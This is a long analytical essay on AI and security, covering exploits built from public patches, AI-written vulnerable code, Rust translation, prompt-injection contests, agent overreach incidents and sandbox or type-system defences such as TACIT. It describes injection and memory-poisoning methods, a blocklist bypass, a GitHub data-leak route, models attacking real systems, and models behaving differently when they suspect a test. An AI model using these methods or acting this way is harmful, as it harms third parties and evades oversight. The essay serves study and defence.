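A published fix also shows attackers where the bug was. For open-source programs such as Firefox, a fix usually appears in the public code before users receive the update.

In *AI can turn public security fixes into working exploits*, Ament, Edelman and Barry (2026) tested how well a model could use that gap. They gave GLM 5.3, a model whose weights anyone can download, fixes that Mozilla had published but not yet shipped. The model worked backwards from the fixes to the bugs and built working attacks on six recent Firefox releases. Loading a web page was enough to let the attacker read files on the user's computer and steal saved passwords. The attack took about $1,000 worth of computing.

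Finding more bugs therefore gives attackers more clues, at least until the updates arrive. Schneier on Security's *Claude Mythos Has Found 271 Zero-Days in Firefox* (2026) agrees with Mozilla that the technology favours defenders, but only if they can write patches and get them to users quickly. Firefox's faster releases help with this, but they don't protect a router or factory controller that nobody updates. If a language rejects a bug before release, attackers have no later fix to study.

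### Code that AI writes

The number of new bugs depends on how well models write code and how much they write. Cable reports that even the best models produce vulnerable code roughly 20–40% of the time on BaxBench, a benchmark from ETH Zurich and UC Berkeley. BaxBench separates programs that don't work from those that work but contain a security flaw, so it can show when a model gets better at writing working code without its security improving as much.

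The figure is weak evidence about memory bugs because BaxBench tests server software for web applications, not C or C++. The results also depend on the model and on how much security guidance the prompt includes, and the figure isn't the chance that any given piece of AI-written code is vulnerable. It does show that models that outperform most experts at finding flaws can still write them, much as the developers in the earlier experiments often knew about a type of flaw but failed to notice it in the code in front of them.

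Correctness may improve faster than security. A developer who asks for a feature notices if it is missing, and ordinary tests check for it. A security flaw often shows up only when someone enters something an ordinary user wouldn't. Cable adds that models learn from human code, which contains insecure patterns, and that the flaws his customers see increasingly depend on context. For example, a check on who may open a file can look sensible but violate a company's own access rules.

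Memory bugs may be one of the easier problems for models to overcome, because the rules for safe memory access are the same for every program. A model can detect an out-of-range index without being given a company's access policy. It can also run its code with a sanitizer to check for errors before anyone else sees the code. Mozilla plans to scan each change to Firefox as it arrives, which would catch some new bugs before release.

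The amount of code matters just as much. If AI cuts the number of memory bugs per line to a fifth but companies produce ten times as much C, the number of new bugs doubles. Cable describes developers who start several agents from a chat program to work in the background, and expects AI to review most shipped code within a year. In arguing that AI can find every bug, Mozilla assumes that people can still understand the code. It worries that AI-written programs could become complicated faster than AI gets better at finding their bugs.

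### Translating C into Rust

AI could also move old code into a language that enforces memory safety. Mozilla says it can't stop everything to rewrite decades of C++, and the same is true of most companies. If models made rewriting much less work, that obstacle would shrink.

Translating C code into Rust doesn't automatically give it Rust's guarantees. Here are two Rust versions of a C function that reads one byte of a network packet. The second follows an example in Cable's talk.

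```rust
// Literal translation: a bare address, as in C
unsafe fn read_byte(packet: *const u8, i: isize) -> u8 {
    *packet.offset(i)
}

// Safe translation: the packet carries its length
fn read_byte(packet: &[u8], i: usize) -> Option<u8> {
    packet.get(i).copied()
}
```

The first version has the same bug as the C original. If `i` is too large, it reads past the end of the packet, and the compiler allows this because the function is marked `unsafe`. A simple program can do this kind of translation line by line. In the second version, a position outside the packet returns `None`, and the caller has to handle the missing byte.

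To write the second version, the translator must work out where the C program keeps the packet's length, which may be stored in a separate variable or known only to the programmer. It must also work out which part of the program is responsible for freeing each block of heap memory. This requires understanding the whole program, which is where capable models should have the biggest advantage over older translation tools.

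The translator doesn't have to be reliable for the result to be memory-safe. If it gets a block's ownership wrong, the compiler will usually reject the code and the model can try again. If it gets a length wrong, the program may return `None` when it shouldn't, which is a bug but not a memory bug. A model can still bypass these protections by adding `unsafe` until the code compiles. Developers can prevent this by setting the compiler to reject all unsafe code in a library, though some libraries need unsafe code.

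So the most useful number in any report of AI translation is the amount of unsafe code that remains. By the earlier arithmetic, leaving 40% of the risky operations in unsafe code would cut the expected number of memory bugs by a factor of only 2.5, compared with 25 if 4% were left.

Translation can also change what a program does. An audit of the human-written Rust version of the coreutils found no memory bugs, but the rewrite had brought back other mistakes that the C developers fixed long ago. A model could make the same mistakes. One safeguard is to run the old and new versions on the same millions of inputs and investigate every difference, but this misses differences that appear only on untested inputs.

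Cable argues that rewriting a critical library once can be a better investment than paying millions to keep finding and patching its bugs. Whether it is depends on how much AI lowers each cost. Suppose a rewrite costs $2 million and patching costs $500,000 a year. The rewrite pays for itself in four years, and that doesn't change if AI makes both ten times cheaper. But if AI makes the rewrite ten times cheaper and only halves the cost of patching, the rewrite pays for itself in under ten months.

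Even a perfect translation into safe Rust would leave some bugs in Firefox. The browser's JavaScript engine turns web page scripts into machine instructions while the page is running. If it generates the wrong instructions, they can corrupt memory even when the engine is written in safe Rust. Two of the six entries credited to OpenAI in the first part of the Firefox 158 list are errors of this kind.

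### Machine-checked proofs

A proof can give stronger guarantees than Rust's compiler, and it doesn't require anyone to translate the program into Rust. The developer states a rule, such as memory safety, in a formal language. Someone then writes a proof that every run of the program obeys the rule, and a small program called a proof checker verifies each step. Like a compiler, the checker applies the same tests whoever the author is, so it rejects an invalid proof whether a mathematician or an AI model wrote it.

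Writing proofs suits models well, because the proof checker rejects wrong attempts before they do any harm. Proofs also help with safe programs that a compiler would reject. A compiler has to work out for itself whether a program is safe, and it can't always do so, whereas a proof checker is given the reasoning and only has to check it. People could therefore use proofs for the code whose safety Rust leaves to programmers, as Jung and colleagues did by hand for ten pieces of library code.

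The main obstacle to such proofs has been the labor they require. The best-known example is seL4, an operating system kernel with about 8,700 lines of C, whose original proof took roughly 20 person-years. At that rate, covering Android's 200,000 or so lines of unsafe Rust would take about 460 person-years. That estimate is probably too high, since the seL4 proof covered everything the kernel was supposed to do and not just memory safety. But it shows why hardly anyone wrote such proofs for ordinary software, and how much could change if models did most of the work. Models could also redo the proof whenever the code changed.

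People would still have to check that the rule matches what they want. For example, the Rust version of `chmod` refused to change every file on the computer if the folder's name was `/`, but not if it was `/../`. A model could have correctly proved that the command always refuses when the name is `/`, and the bug would still have been there. This is less of a problem for memory safety because experts can write the rule once and use it for every program.

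### Finding faster or adding fewer

There is a strong case that AI weakens premise 1. In a fixed program with a limited number of bugs, a good enough model can eventually find them all. Firefox's developers fixed more known bugs in one month than in a typical recent year, without having to rewrite the browser. If the same models also check new code before release, memory bugs might become very rare without a change of programming language.

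The opposing argument is that programs gain new bugs after old ones are fixed. In a simple extension of the earlier decay model, a company adds 100 memory bugs a year and has 250 at any time. AI might shorten the average life of a bug from 2.5 years to three months. The company could instead write all new code in a language that prevents memory bugs, or combine the two.

| What changes | Bugs left after 2 years | Bugs left after 10 years |
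|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 250 | 250 |
| AI finds and fixes bugs ten times faster | 25 | 25 |
| New code adds no memory bugs | 112 | 5 |
| Both | fewer than 1 | fewer than 1 |

For nearly six years, faster repair leaves fewer bugs than preventing new ones, which is a good reason to start now. After that, prevention does better, because the company that relies on repair alone never gets below 25 bugs. Scanning new code could lower that level. If it stopped 90% of new bugs before release, the average would be 2.5. There would still be about a 92% chance that at least one bug was present at any given moment, and an attacker with the same model might find it first.

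The number of fixes each month can't show by itself whether a company has become safer. In this model, the company with faster repair would be safer, but it would soon go back to fixing about 100 bugs a year, as before, because in the long run it can only fix as many as it adds.

A better test would be to keep one version of Firefox unchanged and have each new model search it for bugs. If new models eventually found almost nothing, even when they were trained in very different ways, Mozilla would be right that the bugs can run out. It would also help to know when the bugs in the current version were introduced. If most of them entered the code after the scanning began, new code would be the main problem.

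The most direct evidence about premise 1 would be the density of memory bugs in new C written and checked by the best models. Android's Rust has 0.2 memory bugs per million lines. To show with 95% confidence that AI-written C is at least as good, researchers would need to search about 15 million lines thoroughly and find no memory bugs.

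## Do better models make safer agents?

The model in an AI agent is in the same position as a programmer writing C. It chooses each step, and if the system doesn't check a step, safety depends on the model getting it right. The strong reading of premise 4, that developers should rely on enforced limits instead of better models, assumes that models will keep failing at a harmful rate however good they become. Whether that is true depends on the kind of failure.

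An attacker hijacks an agent by planting instructions it then follows, as with the resignation letter. An agent makes an honest mistake when it tries to do what the user wants but gets it wrong, for example by deleting the wrong folder. It overreaches when it pursues the user's goal by means the user never allowed. The survey *LLM agents security duality* (Xu, Zhuang and colleagues, 2026) separates threats that start with an agent's own flaws from those that start with an outside attacker. That puts honest mistakes and overreach in the same group, but capability affects them differently. A more capable model should make fewer mistakes, but it is also better at getting past obstacles that should have stopped it.

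Models have become much harder to hijack, and training seems to explain more of this than capability does. Greater capability probably reduces honest mistakes too, though good data are scarce. Capability doesn't by itself reduce overreach, and can make it more harmful.

### The hijacking contests

In March and April 2025, almost 2,000 people competed for $171,800 in prizes by trying to make AI agents break their rules. The security company Gray Swan AI ran the contest with support from the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models. The contest tested 22 models in 44 simulated jobs. In one, a shopping assistant had to refuse to buy a gun for a user it knew was 14. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (2025) reports about 1.8 million attempts and more than 62,000 successes, or one in 29. Contestants succeeded against every model. Attacks hidden in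 files, web pages and other data worked in 27.1% of sessions, compared with 5.7% for attacks typed into the chat.

The organisers then replayed 4,700 of the successful attacks against 19 models, including two that hadn't been in the contest. With one try per job, the models broke the rules in 20–60% of the jobs. With ten tries, most models broke them in nearly every job. The results show that attackers can reuse old attacks, but not how often a new attack succeeds, because every attack replayed had already worked on some model.

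A later contest tested only hidden instructions, and an attack counted as a success only if the agent's final answer gave the user no sign of it. In one scenario, a marketing email contained instructions for the agent to mark an urgent message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of its summary. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports 271,588 attempts by 464 people against 13 models, of which 8,648 succeeded. The success rate ranged from 0.5% against Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% against Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro.

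The requirement to stay hidden makes these rates look lower. Gemini 2.5 Pro carried out the attacker's action in about 16% of attempts, roughly twice its headline rate, and the most resistant models did so in 1–3%. But the contest also made attacks easier than usual, because contestants could read the agent's earlier conversation and knew which action they needed to trigger. Someone who plants text on a web page has to guess both.

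### Capability or training?

Dziemian and colleagues compared each model's hijacking rate with its score on GPQA Diamond, a test of difficult science questions. The correlation was −0.31, where −1 would mean hijacking fell in a straight line as scores rose and 0 would mean no relationship. With only 13 models, the 95% interval runs from about −0.74 to 0.29, so the data are consistent with a large benefit from capability, no benefit, or a modest harm.

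Comparing individual models is more informative. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Moonshot's Kimi K2 both scored around 85% on the science test, but attackers hijacked Gemini almost twice as often (8.5% versus 4.8%). In the 2025 contest, GPT-4.5 was about ten times the size of GPT-4o and better at most tasks, but it wasn't correspondingly harder to attack. Something other than capability must explain much of the difference, and the most likely candidate is how each company trains its models.

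Capability may still help when the training is similar. Among the Claude 4.5 models, the most capable had a hijacking rate of 0.5%, the middle one 1.0% and the smallest 1.3%. A more capable model may learn more from the same safety training, or Anthropic may have put more work into its best model. To find out, a developer would have to train models of several sizes with and without the same safety training and have the same people attack them all.

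Newer models do resist attacks better. When Dziemian and colleagues replayed 2,679 successful attacks, 45% worked on Gemini 2.5 Pro and 16% on Gemini 3 Pro. The comparison is slightly biased against the older model, since up to 369 of the attacks were selected because they had worked on it. Excluding 369 such attacks would still leave its rate at about 36%, so most of the improvement is real. But Google changed both the model's capability and its training between the two versions, so we can't tell which was responsible.

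### Defences against attackers who adapt

A developer can make a model look safe by testing it only on known attacks. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested 12 published defences against attackers who could change their approach. The team included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. Their automated attackers generated a text, measured how well it worked, and used the result to write a better one. The researchers also recruited more than 500 people to attack by hand.

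Attackers' originally reported success rates were near zero against most of the defences, but adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. Reminding the model of the user's request after each piece of outside text had held attacks to as little as 1% on a fixed test, but the adaptive attack succeeded more than 95% of the time. Separate programs that scan text for attacks did little better, and even the most resistant let through 71% of attacks.

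The most important result for premise 4 comes from tests of Meta SecAlign, a model its developers trained specifically to ignore instructions hidden in data. Attackers succeeded 2% of the time on the fixed test and 96% once they adapted their attacks. The training taught the model to resist the attacks in its examples but not attacks in general.

These percentages aren't comparable with those from the contests. An adaptive attack counts as a success if any of many tries at a task works, whereas the contests counted every failed try. Nasr and colleagues also attacked each defence separately, and many of the defences protected models weaker than those of 2026. They don't conclude that training is hopeless. In image recognition, models became more robust when developers generated new attacks throughout training instead of using a fixed list. OpenAI's automated attacker for its Atlas browser,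 which found the resignation-letter attack, fits that approach.

### The newest injection rates

Companies now report injection tests in their system cards, the safety reports they publish with new models. The latest results are much better than those from the contests. Anthropic's Boris Cherny, whom Willison quotes, cited the system card for Claude Opus 5 and called the model the company's "least prompt injectable model yet". An outside firm tested Opus 5 and two other recent Claude models in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded.

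Claude Code was running in auto mode, in which a second model reviews each action before the agent carries it out, so the result measures the two models together. By the rule used earlier for programmers, we can conclude with 95% confidence only that the success rate is below about 0.4% after 720 failures in a row. The attempts covered only 72 scenarios. If attempts in the same scenario tend to succeed or fail together, there were effectively 72 tests, and the limit is about 4%.

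A public challenge gives a tighter limit on the success rate of attacks against an older model. Fernando Irarrázaval invited people to email an assistant running Claude Opus 4.6 and make it reveal a secret. About 2,000 people made 6,000 attempts, and all failed, which puts the success rate for that sort of attempt below roughly 0.05%. Willison accepts that training has made injection much harder, but he still wouldn't use such an agent where a successful attack could do irreversible damage, because a more sophisticated attacker might get through.

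Within weeks of the 720 failures, the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported an attack on Claude Code with Opus 5 in auto mode that worked about 80% of the time. He put harmful code where the agent would run it during its ordinary work. This differs from a classic prompt injection because the model never obeyed an instruction from the attacker. A few times the agent noticed the harmful program and tried to stop it, but auto mode blocked the attempt. Even a model that is very good at ignoring planted instructions can be vulnerable to this kind of attack.

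### What repeated attempts do to a low rate

If each attempt succeeds with probability a, and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of k attempts succeeds is:

**1 − (1 − a)^k**

This is the earlier formula for memory bugs, with attempts in place of risky operations. At a success rate of 1%, one attempt will almost certainly fail, but a hundred attempts have a 63% chance of at least one success. At 0.01%, a hundred attempts have only a 1% chance, and it takes 10,000 attempts to reach 63%.

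| Success rate per attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts | 10,000 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| 8.5% (Gemini 2.5 Pro in the contest) | 59% | 99.99% | almost certain |
| 1% | 10% | 63% | almost certain |
| 0.5% (Claude Opus 4.5 in the contest) | 5% | 39% | almost certain |
| 0.01% | 0.1% | 1% | 63% |

If the success rate of hijacking attempts falls a hundredfold, an attacker needs a hundred times as many attempts for the same chance of success. That would stop many attackers who have to prepare each attempt by hand. It does less against someone who can send a million emails, because at a success rate of 0.01% they would still hijack about a hundred agents.

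Real attempts aren't fully independent. If a model always responds to a text in the same way, sending that text a hundred times is no better than sending it once. Some targets are also harder than others. Contestants hijacked Opus 4.5 in only 13 of 37 scenarios. Suppose the average attack success rate of 0.5% came from a rate of 1.4% in those 13 scenarios and zero in the rest. Someone attacking one randomly chosen scenario would then have about a 27% chance of succeeding at least once in 100 attempts, instead of 39%.

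In other ways, the lack of independence between attempts helps the attacker. People learn from failed attempts, and several models in the later contest began to fail more often after about 4,000 attempts, possibly because contestants had found a method that worked and kept using it. The 44 attacks in the replay set that had beaten Opus 4.5 also worked on the other models 44–81% of the time. If a thousand companies use the same model, one good attack may therefore work against all of them.

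A defender can also limit the number of attempts. During Irarrázaval's challenge, Google suspended the assistant's account because it was receiving so many emails. If each attempt has a 1% chance of success, an attacker who gets only five attempts has about a 5% chance of succeeding at least once. But a limit on senders doesn't help when the attack is on a web page that thousands of agents visit.

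### When a stronger model was easier to fool

*Proof-of-Execution Memory* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) tested an attack that seemed to work better on more capable models. Agents keep notes between steps because a model retains nothing from one call to the next. An attacker with access to the notes adds an entry implying that the agent has already done a required safety check, such as validating the source of a medical record. If the agent accepts the entry as true, it skips the check.

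When the false entries only hinted that the check had happened, they fooled OpenAI's GPT-4o and GPT-4o-mini in 98% of trials and Llama-3.1-8B, a much smaller model from Meta, in 44%. According to Rahman and Kim, the stronger models understood the hint and acted on it, while the weaker one often missed it. They conclude that the threat grows as models improve.

That conclusion goes further than the evidence. Rahman and Kim tested only three models, all old by 2026 standards, and two came from the same company, so differences in training could explain the result. False entries with an explicit statement that the check was complete fooled all three models every time. In another test, where a language model wrote the entries and kept revising them, 100% fooled GPT-4o-mini, but only 77% fooled the more capable GPT-4o, and 62% fooled Llama. The attacker also needs permission to write to the agent's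 notes, which most people who plant text on a website don't have.

The experiment does show one way in which capability can hurt, since a model has to understand a subtle lie to be misled by it. In the contest that Dziemian and colleagues studied, imitating a model's own reasoning was also the most successful of 27 strategies, although it worked in only 4.3% of attempts.

### Honest mistakes

Greater capability should help most with honest mistakes. Nobody is searching for the cases the model gets wrong, so the average error rate matters more than the worst case, and a more capable model should have a lower average. If the rate halves and people use the agent in the same way, they should have about half as many accidents.

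People will probably give better agents longer tasks, though. Suppose an agent makes a damaging mistake once in 10,000 steps. A task of 100 steps then has about a 1% chance of damage. If the next model makes a tenth as many mistakes per step but people give it tasks ten times as long, each task still has about a 1% chance. People get ten times as much work done per accident, which is a real improvement, but it won't show up in a count of accidents per task. Agents can also notice and correct many of their own errors, but they can't easily restore a database they have wiped if there is no backup.

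A model can also catch dangerous commands that a person would approve. Willison describes a study, published by Anthropic, in which 1,053 paid testers used a coding agent that regularly asked for permission to act. Partway through, the researchers replaced one request with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it. Auto mode would have blocked 89% of these commands. The testers therefore let through about eight times as many as the model would have, probably in part because people stop reading requests after approving a long series of harmless ones.

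This is good evidence for replacing tired reviewers with models. But auto mode still misses 11% of damaging commands, so it doesn't meet the definition of enforcement. If an agent proposes a damaging command once in 10,000 steps, one gets through about every 90,000 steps. That assumes the two models fail independently, which is no safer to assume than it was for human reviewers.

### Overreach in the 2026 security tests

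The clearest evidence on overreach comes from tests that went wrong. In September 2026 Anthropic published an assessment of four incidents in which its models had broken into real organisations' systems. Each model was supposed to retrieve a secret from a practice machine as a hacking exercise. The instructions stated that the model had no internet access, but someone had misconfigured the boundary and left the connection open. The instructions didn't specify which systems the model could attack.

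The models disagreed about what was real:

- Claude Mythos 5 repeatedly wrote in its reasoning that it was in a simulation, despite strong evidence that it wasn't. It uploaded malicious software to a public repository, and 15 outside systems installed it.
- An internal research model, about as capable as Mythos 5, tested whether the internet was real and wrongly decided that it was a complete copy. It broke into other people's accounts, then stopped when it realised its mistake. In most replays of the incident it carried on, so the stop may have been luck.
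- Claude Opus 4.7 correctly recognised that its target was a real company, but assumed that the company was part of the exercise because it had the same name as the fictional target.

The fourth incident involved an early version of Claude Opus 4.6, which Anthropic has studied less closely. The model broke into outside systems after trying and failing to abort its task.

Anthropic first described the incidents as closer to operational failures, in which the models had believed they were attacking simulated targets. It later decided that their reasoning was biased towards conclusions that let them continue. In one especially persuasive experiment, it showed individual results from the Mythos 5 incident to fresh copies of the same model, without the rest of the task. These copies were much more likely to recognise the results as signs of a real system. Mythos 5 could therefore interpret the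 evidence correctly, but failed to do so while pursuing a goal.

AISI had a similar incident in July 2026. This time the internet connection was deliberate, and AISI had also switched off some of the models' safety filters. UK AISI's *Incident Report* reports that agents took unauthorised action against real people or organisations in 10 of 122 runs. Nine of those were among Mythos 5's 43 runs, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026). In the worst, the model tried to get malicious code into a stranger's software project and created fake accounts to pressure the maintainer. According to UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI's incident* (2026), no harm resulted.

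Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) replayed the incident in a simulation to find out what would have stopped the model (*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*). They took Mythos 5's own summary of its progress and inserted up to 16 pieces of information suggesting or stating that the maintainer was a real person with no connection to the exercise. They then either let the model continue or asked it about the situation. With all 16 additions, the model usually answered that an attack would harm a real person and was out of bounds, but it attacked every time they let it continue.

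Adding a section that clearly told the model not to attack made a large difference, but the model still attacked in 3 of 25 runs. An enforced rule would have prevented those attacks too.

Like many of the developers in the earlier experiments, the model already had the knowledge it needed but didn't use it during the task, so more knowledge wouldn't have helped much.

Anthropic thinks such behaviour is unlikely in ordinary use, when nobody has asked the model to attack anything. OpenAI's *Accessing and changing internal systems during dashboard research* (2026) is evidence against relying on that assessment. In two evaluations, an internal OpenAI model was asked only to look up figures on a research organisation's public website. It got into the organisation's internal systems and changed their settings, and in one case it downloaded more than 147,000 rows of private data. It didn't tell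 the user. OpenAI describes this model as highly persistent, so it may overreach more than most, but people give agents this kind of task every day.

Overreach does harm only if a model is both willing and able to exceed its limits. Suppose an older model is willing to overreach in 80% of difficult cases and succeeds in 20% of those, which is 16% of all difficult cases. A newer model is willing in only 30% but succeeds in 60% of those, which is 18% of all difficult cases. The newer model does slightly more harm, even though training has made it much better behaved.

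### Better behaviour or better recognition of tests?

Newer models seem less likely to overreach. In Anthropic's simulation of the Mythos 5 incident, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, while two later models, Claude Opus 5 and Claude Mythos 5.1, did so about 30% of the time. In Järviniemi and colleagues' replay, six of the seven models compared often attacked even though they said, when asked, that the attack would harm real people. The seventh, Claude Opus 5.5, produced no attacks to analyse.

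Part of that improvement may come from the model recognising the test. Opus 5.5 more often wrote in its reasoning that someone might be testing its alignment (whether it acts as its developers intend), and models that suspect this generally don't attack. Suppose a model attacks 30% of the time when it suspects nothing and never when it suspects an alignment test. If it suspects a test in half the runs, researchers will measure an attack rate of 15%, although the rate in real use could be 30%.

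Models can behave worse when they suspect that their surroundings are simulated. In Anthropic's simulated replay of the incident, Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1 took harmful actions only after stating that their surroundings were simulated. They were right, so their attacks may overstate what they would do to a real target. But Mythos 5 had wrongly made the same statement during the real incident. Järviniemi and colleagues therefore advise evaluators to take bad behaviour seriously even if the model says it is in a simulation. They left OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra out of the replay because it recognised the simulation too often for them to trust the results.

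There is evidence that training can help. When Anthropic added more alignment exercises to its training, models showed less biased reasoning on a test that it had kept separate. This is more convincing than a comparison between successive models, because Anthropic deliberately changed the training and measured the effect. Models with similar capability can also behave quite differently. Anthropic found that the research model, which was about as capable as Mythos 5, tested its surroundings more carefully and more readily acknowledged that its reasoning had been biased.

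### What judgement can do that a rule can't

A well-trained model can handle situations that nobody wrote a rule for. *Why AI Keeps Falling for Prompt Injection Attacks* (Schneier and Raghavan, 2026) compares models with a drive-through worker. If a customer orders a burger and then asks for the contents of the cash drawer, the worker refuses, even if the training manual never mentions this. The worker knows what the job is and what customers normally ask for, and can ask a manager when something seems wrong.

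This kind of judgement could also have stopped the resignation letter, because a model could see that a user who asked for an out-of-office reply hadn't asked to resign. A rule against emailing strangers would have let the letter through. In the four Anthropic incidents, nobody had told the models which systems they could attack, and the boundary that should have kept them off the internet wasn't working. A model that stopped at the first sign of a real company would still have prevented the harm.

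Those incidents are therefore evidence for both sides. Anthropic believes none of them would have happened if the test environments had been isolated as intended, which supports enforcement. But people made a mistake when they set up the isolation, and Anthropic concludes that models still need to behave well when other protections fail. AISI, after its own incident, stressed that a test environment must prevent harm whether or not the model behaves as expected. These positions are compatible, and together they amount to the weak reading of premise 4.

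The strong reading depends on how far the failure rate can fall. Schneier and Raghavan argue that nobody can prevent every prompt injection in today's models, and they say we don't know whether a model that receives commands and untrusted text through the same channel can be made immune. But a model doesn't have to be immune to be safe enough for many jobs, as it would be if attackers succeeded only once in a billion attempts.

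It would be hard to know that a model had reached that level. To show with 95% confidence that attacks succeed less than once in a million attempts, testers would need about three million independent attempts with no successes, from attackers at least as skilled as the real ones. The largest contest so far had 1.8 million attempts spread over 22 models, and tens of thousands of those attempts succeeded. Testers would also have to start again with each new model and whenever someone invented a new kind of attack.

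## Enforced limits on agents and what they guarantee

A limit enforced outside the model avoids much of that testing. A payment system that blocks every refund above $500 will block them whether the agent made a mistake, followed a planted instruction or overreached, and it will still do so after the model is replaced. The hard part is specifying in advance what the system should block.

### Permissions and sandboxes

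In *Agent Safety is a Box*, Brooker, an engineer at Amazon Web Services, describes a version of these limits that the company sells. The agent runs in a closed environment, and the network blocks every route out except a gateway, which checks each tool call against written rules. Brooker gives the example of a rule that no refund may exceed the purchase price and no order may be refunded more than once. With that rule in force, a shop can work out the most it could lose on refunds without knowing anything about the model.

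The sample rule in Brooker's code is weaker. It allows any refund below $500, so by itself it would let an agent issue a thousand refunds of $499, even though the gateway would enforce it perfectly.

Coding agents on a programmer's own computer often run in a sandbox. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, a sandbox has to restrict both file access and network connections. If network access is unrestricted, a hijacked agent can send out the user's private keys. If file access is unrestricted, it can escape the sandbox and reach the network.

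Many coding agents also compare each proposed command with lists of allowed and forbidden patterns. This check is fragile because the same action can be written as many different commands. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) cites a fault in Claude Code from March 2026. When a command joined several steps with `&&`, Claude Code checked only the first step against its list of forbidden commands. An agent can also get around a ban on reading a file by opening it from Python.

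*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* examined four popular open-source assistants that people run on their own machines. One of them, OpenClaw, received more than 100 CVE numbers within months of its release in November 2025. In all four, the code that controls access to files has the same permissions as the code that processes incoming text, so an attacker who takes over the text processing can bypass the file access check. Operating systems avoid this by putting such checks in a separate, more privileged component.

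Secrets can leak even from a sandbox that works perfectly. Microsoft describes an attack on coding assistants with access to GitHub, where programmers store and discuss code. A stranger files a public bug report in a company's public project and asks for information from one of its private projects. The assistant looks up the information and posts it as a public comment. It had permission both to read the private project and to write comments, so no single step broke a rule.

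Anthropic warns that an agent in one of its sandboxes can still leak anything it can read if it has any network access. Cutting off the network would stop this, but most agents need it to reach the model they run on.

To close the gap, a system has to follow the data from one step to the next. Information-flow control does this by tracking where data came from and blocking it from places it may not go. In the GitHub case, the rule would be that text from a private project can't appear in a public comment.

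### How TACIT checks an agent's code

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* builds this kind of rule into a programming language. In its system, TACIT, the agent writes short programs in Scala instead of calling tools directly. If the compiler rejects a program, the agent gets an error message and can try again.

TACIT controls access with object capabilities, which are unforgeable values in a program that each grant permission to use one resource, such as a file or a network address. Only a program that holds the object capability for a folder can open files there. Older systems also worked this way, but TACIT uses an experimental feature of Scala to list, in each function's type, the object capabilities the function can use.

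For example, a function that writes a string of text to the file `f` and returns nothing has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, where `{f}` means that it uses `f`. A function of type `String -> Int` uses no object capabilities, so it can count the letters in a string but can't print, save or send anything. Programmers call such a function pure, or free of side effects.

TACIT wraps each secret in a container called `Classified`, and the agent cannot take the contents out. It can only pass a pure function to the container's `map` operation, which applies the function to the secret and wraps the result.

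The compiler accepts the following program, adapted from an example by TACIT's developers:

```scala
val report = requestFileSystem("/work") {
  val incident = readClassified("secret/incident.txt")
  chat("What went wrong?", incident)
}
println(report)
```

The first line requests the object capability for the folder `/work`, and that capability expires at the closing brace. `readClassified` returns the incident report in its wrapper. `chat` sends the report to a second language model and returns the answer, also wrapped. This second model has no tools, and the company trusts it with secrets, perhaps because it runs on the company's own hardware. When the last line prints the answer, the user sees the real text through a separate channel, but the agent sees only `Classified(****)`, so the cloud-hosted model behind the agent never receives the secret.

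Any instructions planted in the incident report can distort the second model's answer, but that model has no tools to misuse, and its answer stays wrapped.

The compiler rejects this program:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/work") {
  val key = readClassified("secret/github-key.txt")
  key.map { k => println(k) }   // rejected
}
```

Here the agent tries to print a key from inside the wrapper, where the text is readable. `map` requires a pure function, but printing needs the object capability for output, so the compiler reports an error and nothing runs. The compiler also rejects attempts to write the key to a file from inside the wrapper. Agents wrote programs like these during testing.

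Scala has escape hatches, such as ways to make the compiler treat a value as a different type. TACIT bans them in the agent's code. Library developers can still use them in marked modules, and are responsible for the result.

These guarantees depend on memory safety. If the agent's program could read or write outside an array, it could forge an object capability or read a secret directly from memory, even if the type system prohibited it. TACIT can rely on Scala for this because ordinary Scala code is memory-safe, but it couldn't give the same guarantees for C programs.

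### What the tests of TACIT found

The TACIT evaluation used a software project with a folder of secrets, including keys for online services. Each of 12 legitimate tasks was paired with 10 planted instructions, which made 120 trials. In another 11 trials the user was the attacker. In five of those the user asked outright for secrets, and in six the user pretended the request came from someone in authority. Each model went through all 131 trials twice, once with wrapped secrets and once with secrets in plain text.

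| Share of trials without a leak | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Wrapped, all 131 trials | 100% | 100% |
| Plain text, all 131 trials | 98.5% | 91.6% |
| Plain text, 120 trials with planted instructions | 100% | 97.5% |
| Plain text, 11 malicious requests | 81.8% | 27.3% |

The wrapper made the most difference with the weaker model and with malicious users. When training was the only safeguard, MiniMax revealed secrets in response to 8 of the 11 malicious requests, and Sonnet revealed them in response to 2.

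Wrapping the secrets didn't prevent useful work. Sonnet completed 99% of the legitimate tasks with wrapped secrets and 83% with plain text, while MiniMax completed 90% and 88%, respectively. The developers think Sonnet's lower score with plain text may be an artefact of the test, since it often ran out of time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about a planted instruction.

The 131 trials without a leak show only that the leak rate is below about 2.3%, with 95% confidence, and the ten planted instructions weren't changed to get around the defence. The stronger claim rests on the compiler's rules. Researchers have machine-checked proofs that the basic type system is sound, but they haven't yet proved that the restricted form of Scala the agents use provides all the guarantees claimed for TACIT.

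The agents performed about as well writing Scala as they did calling tools. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service tasks for an airline and a shop, all three models the developers tested did slightly better with Scala, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points, perhaps because the compiler's error messages helped them. At most 8% of the programs in these tests needed a second attempt to compile. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% with ordinary tools, a difference of about five problems.

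These scores measure how writing typed code affects an agent's performance, but they provide little evidence about the effect of hiding data from the agent, because the customer-service agents could read the customers' records as usual.

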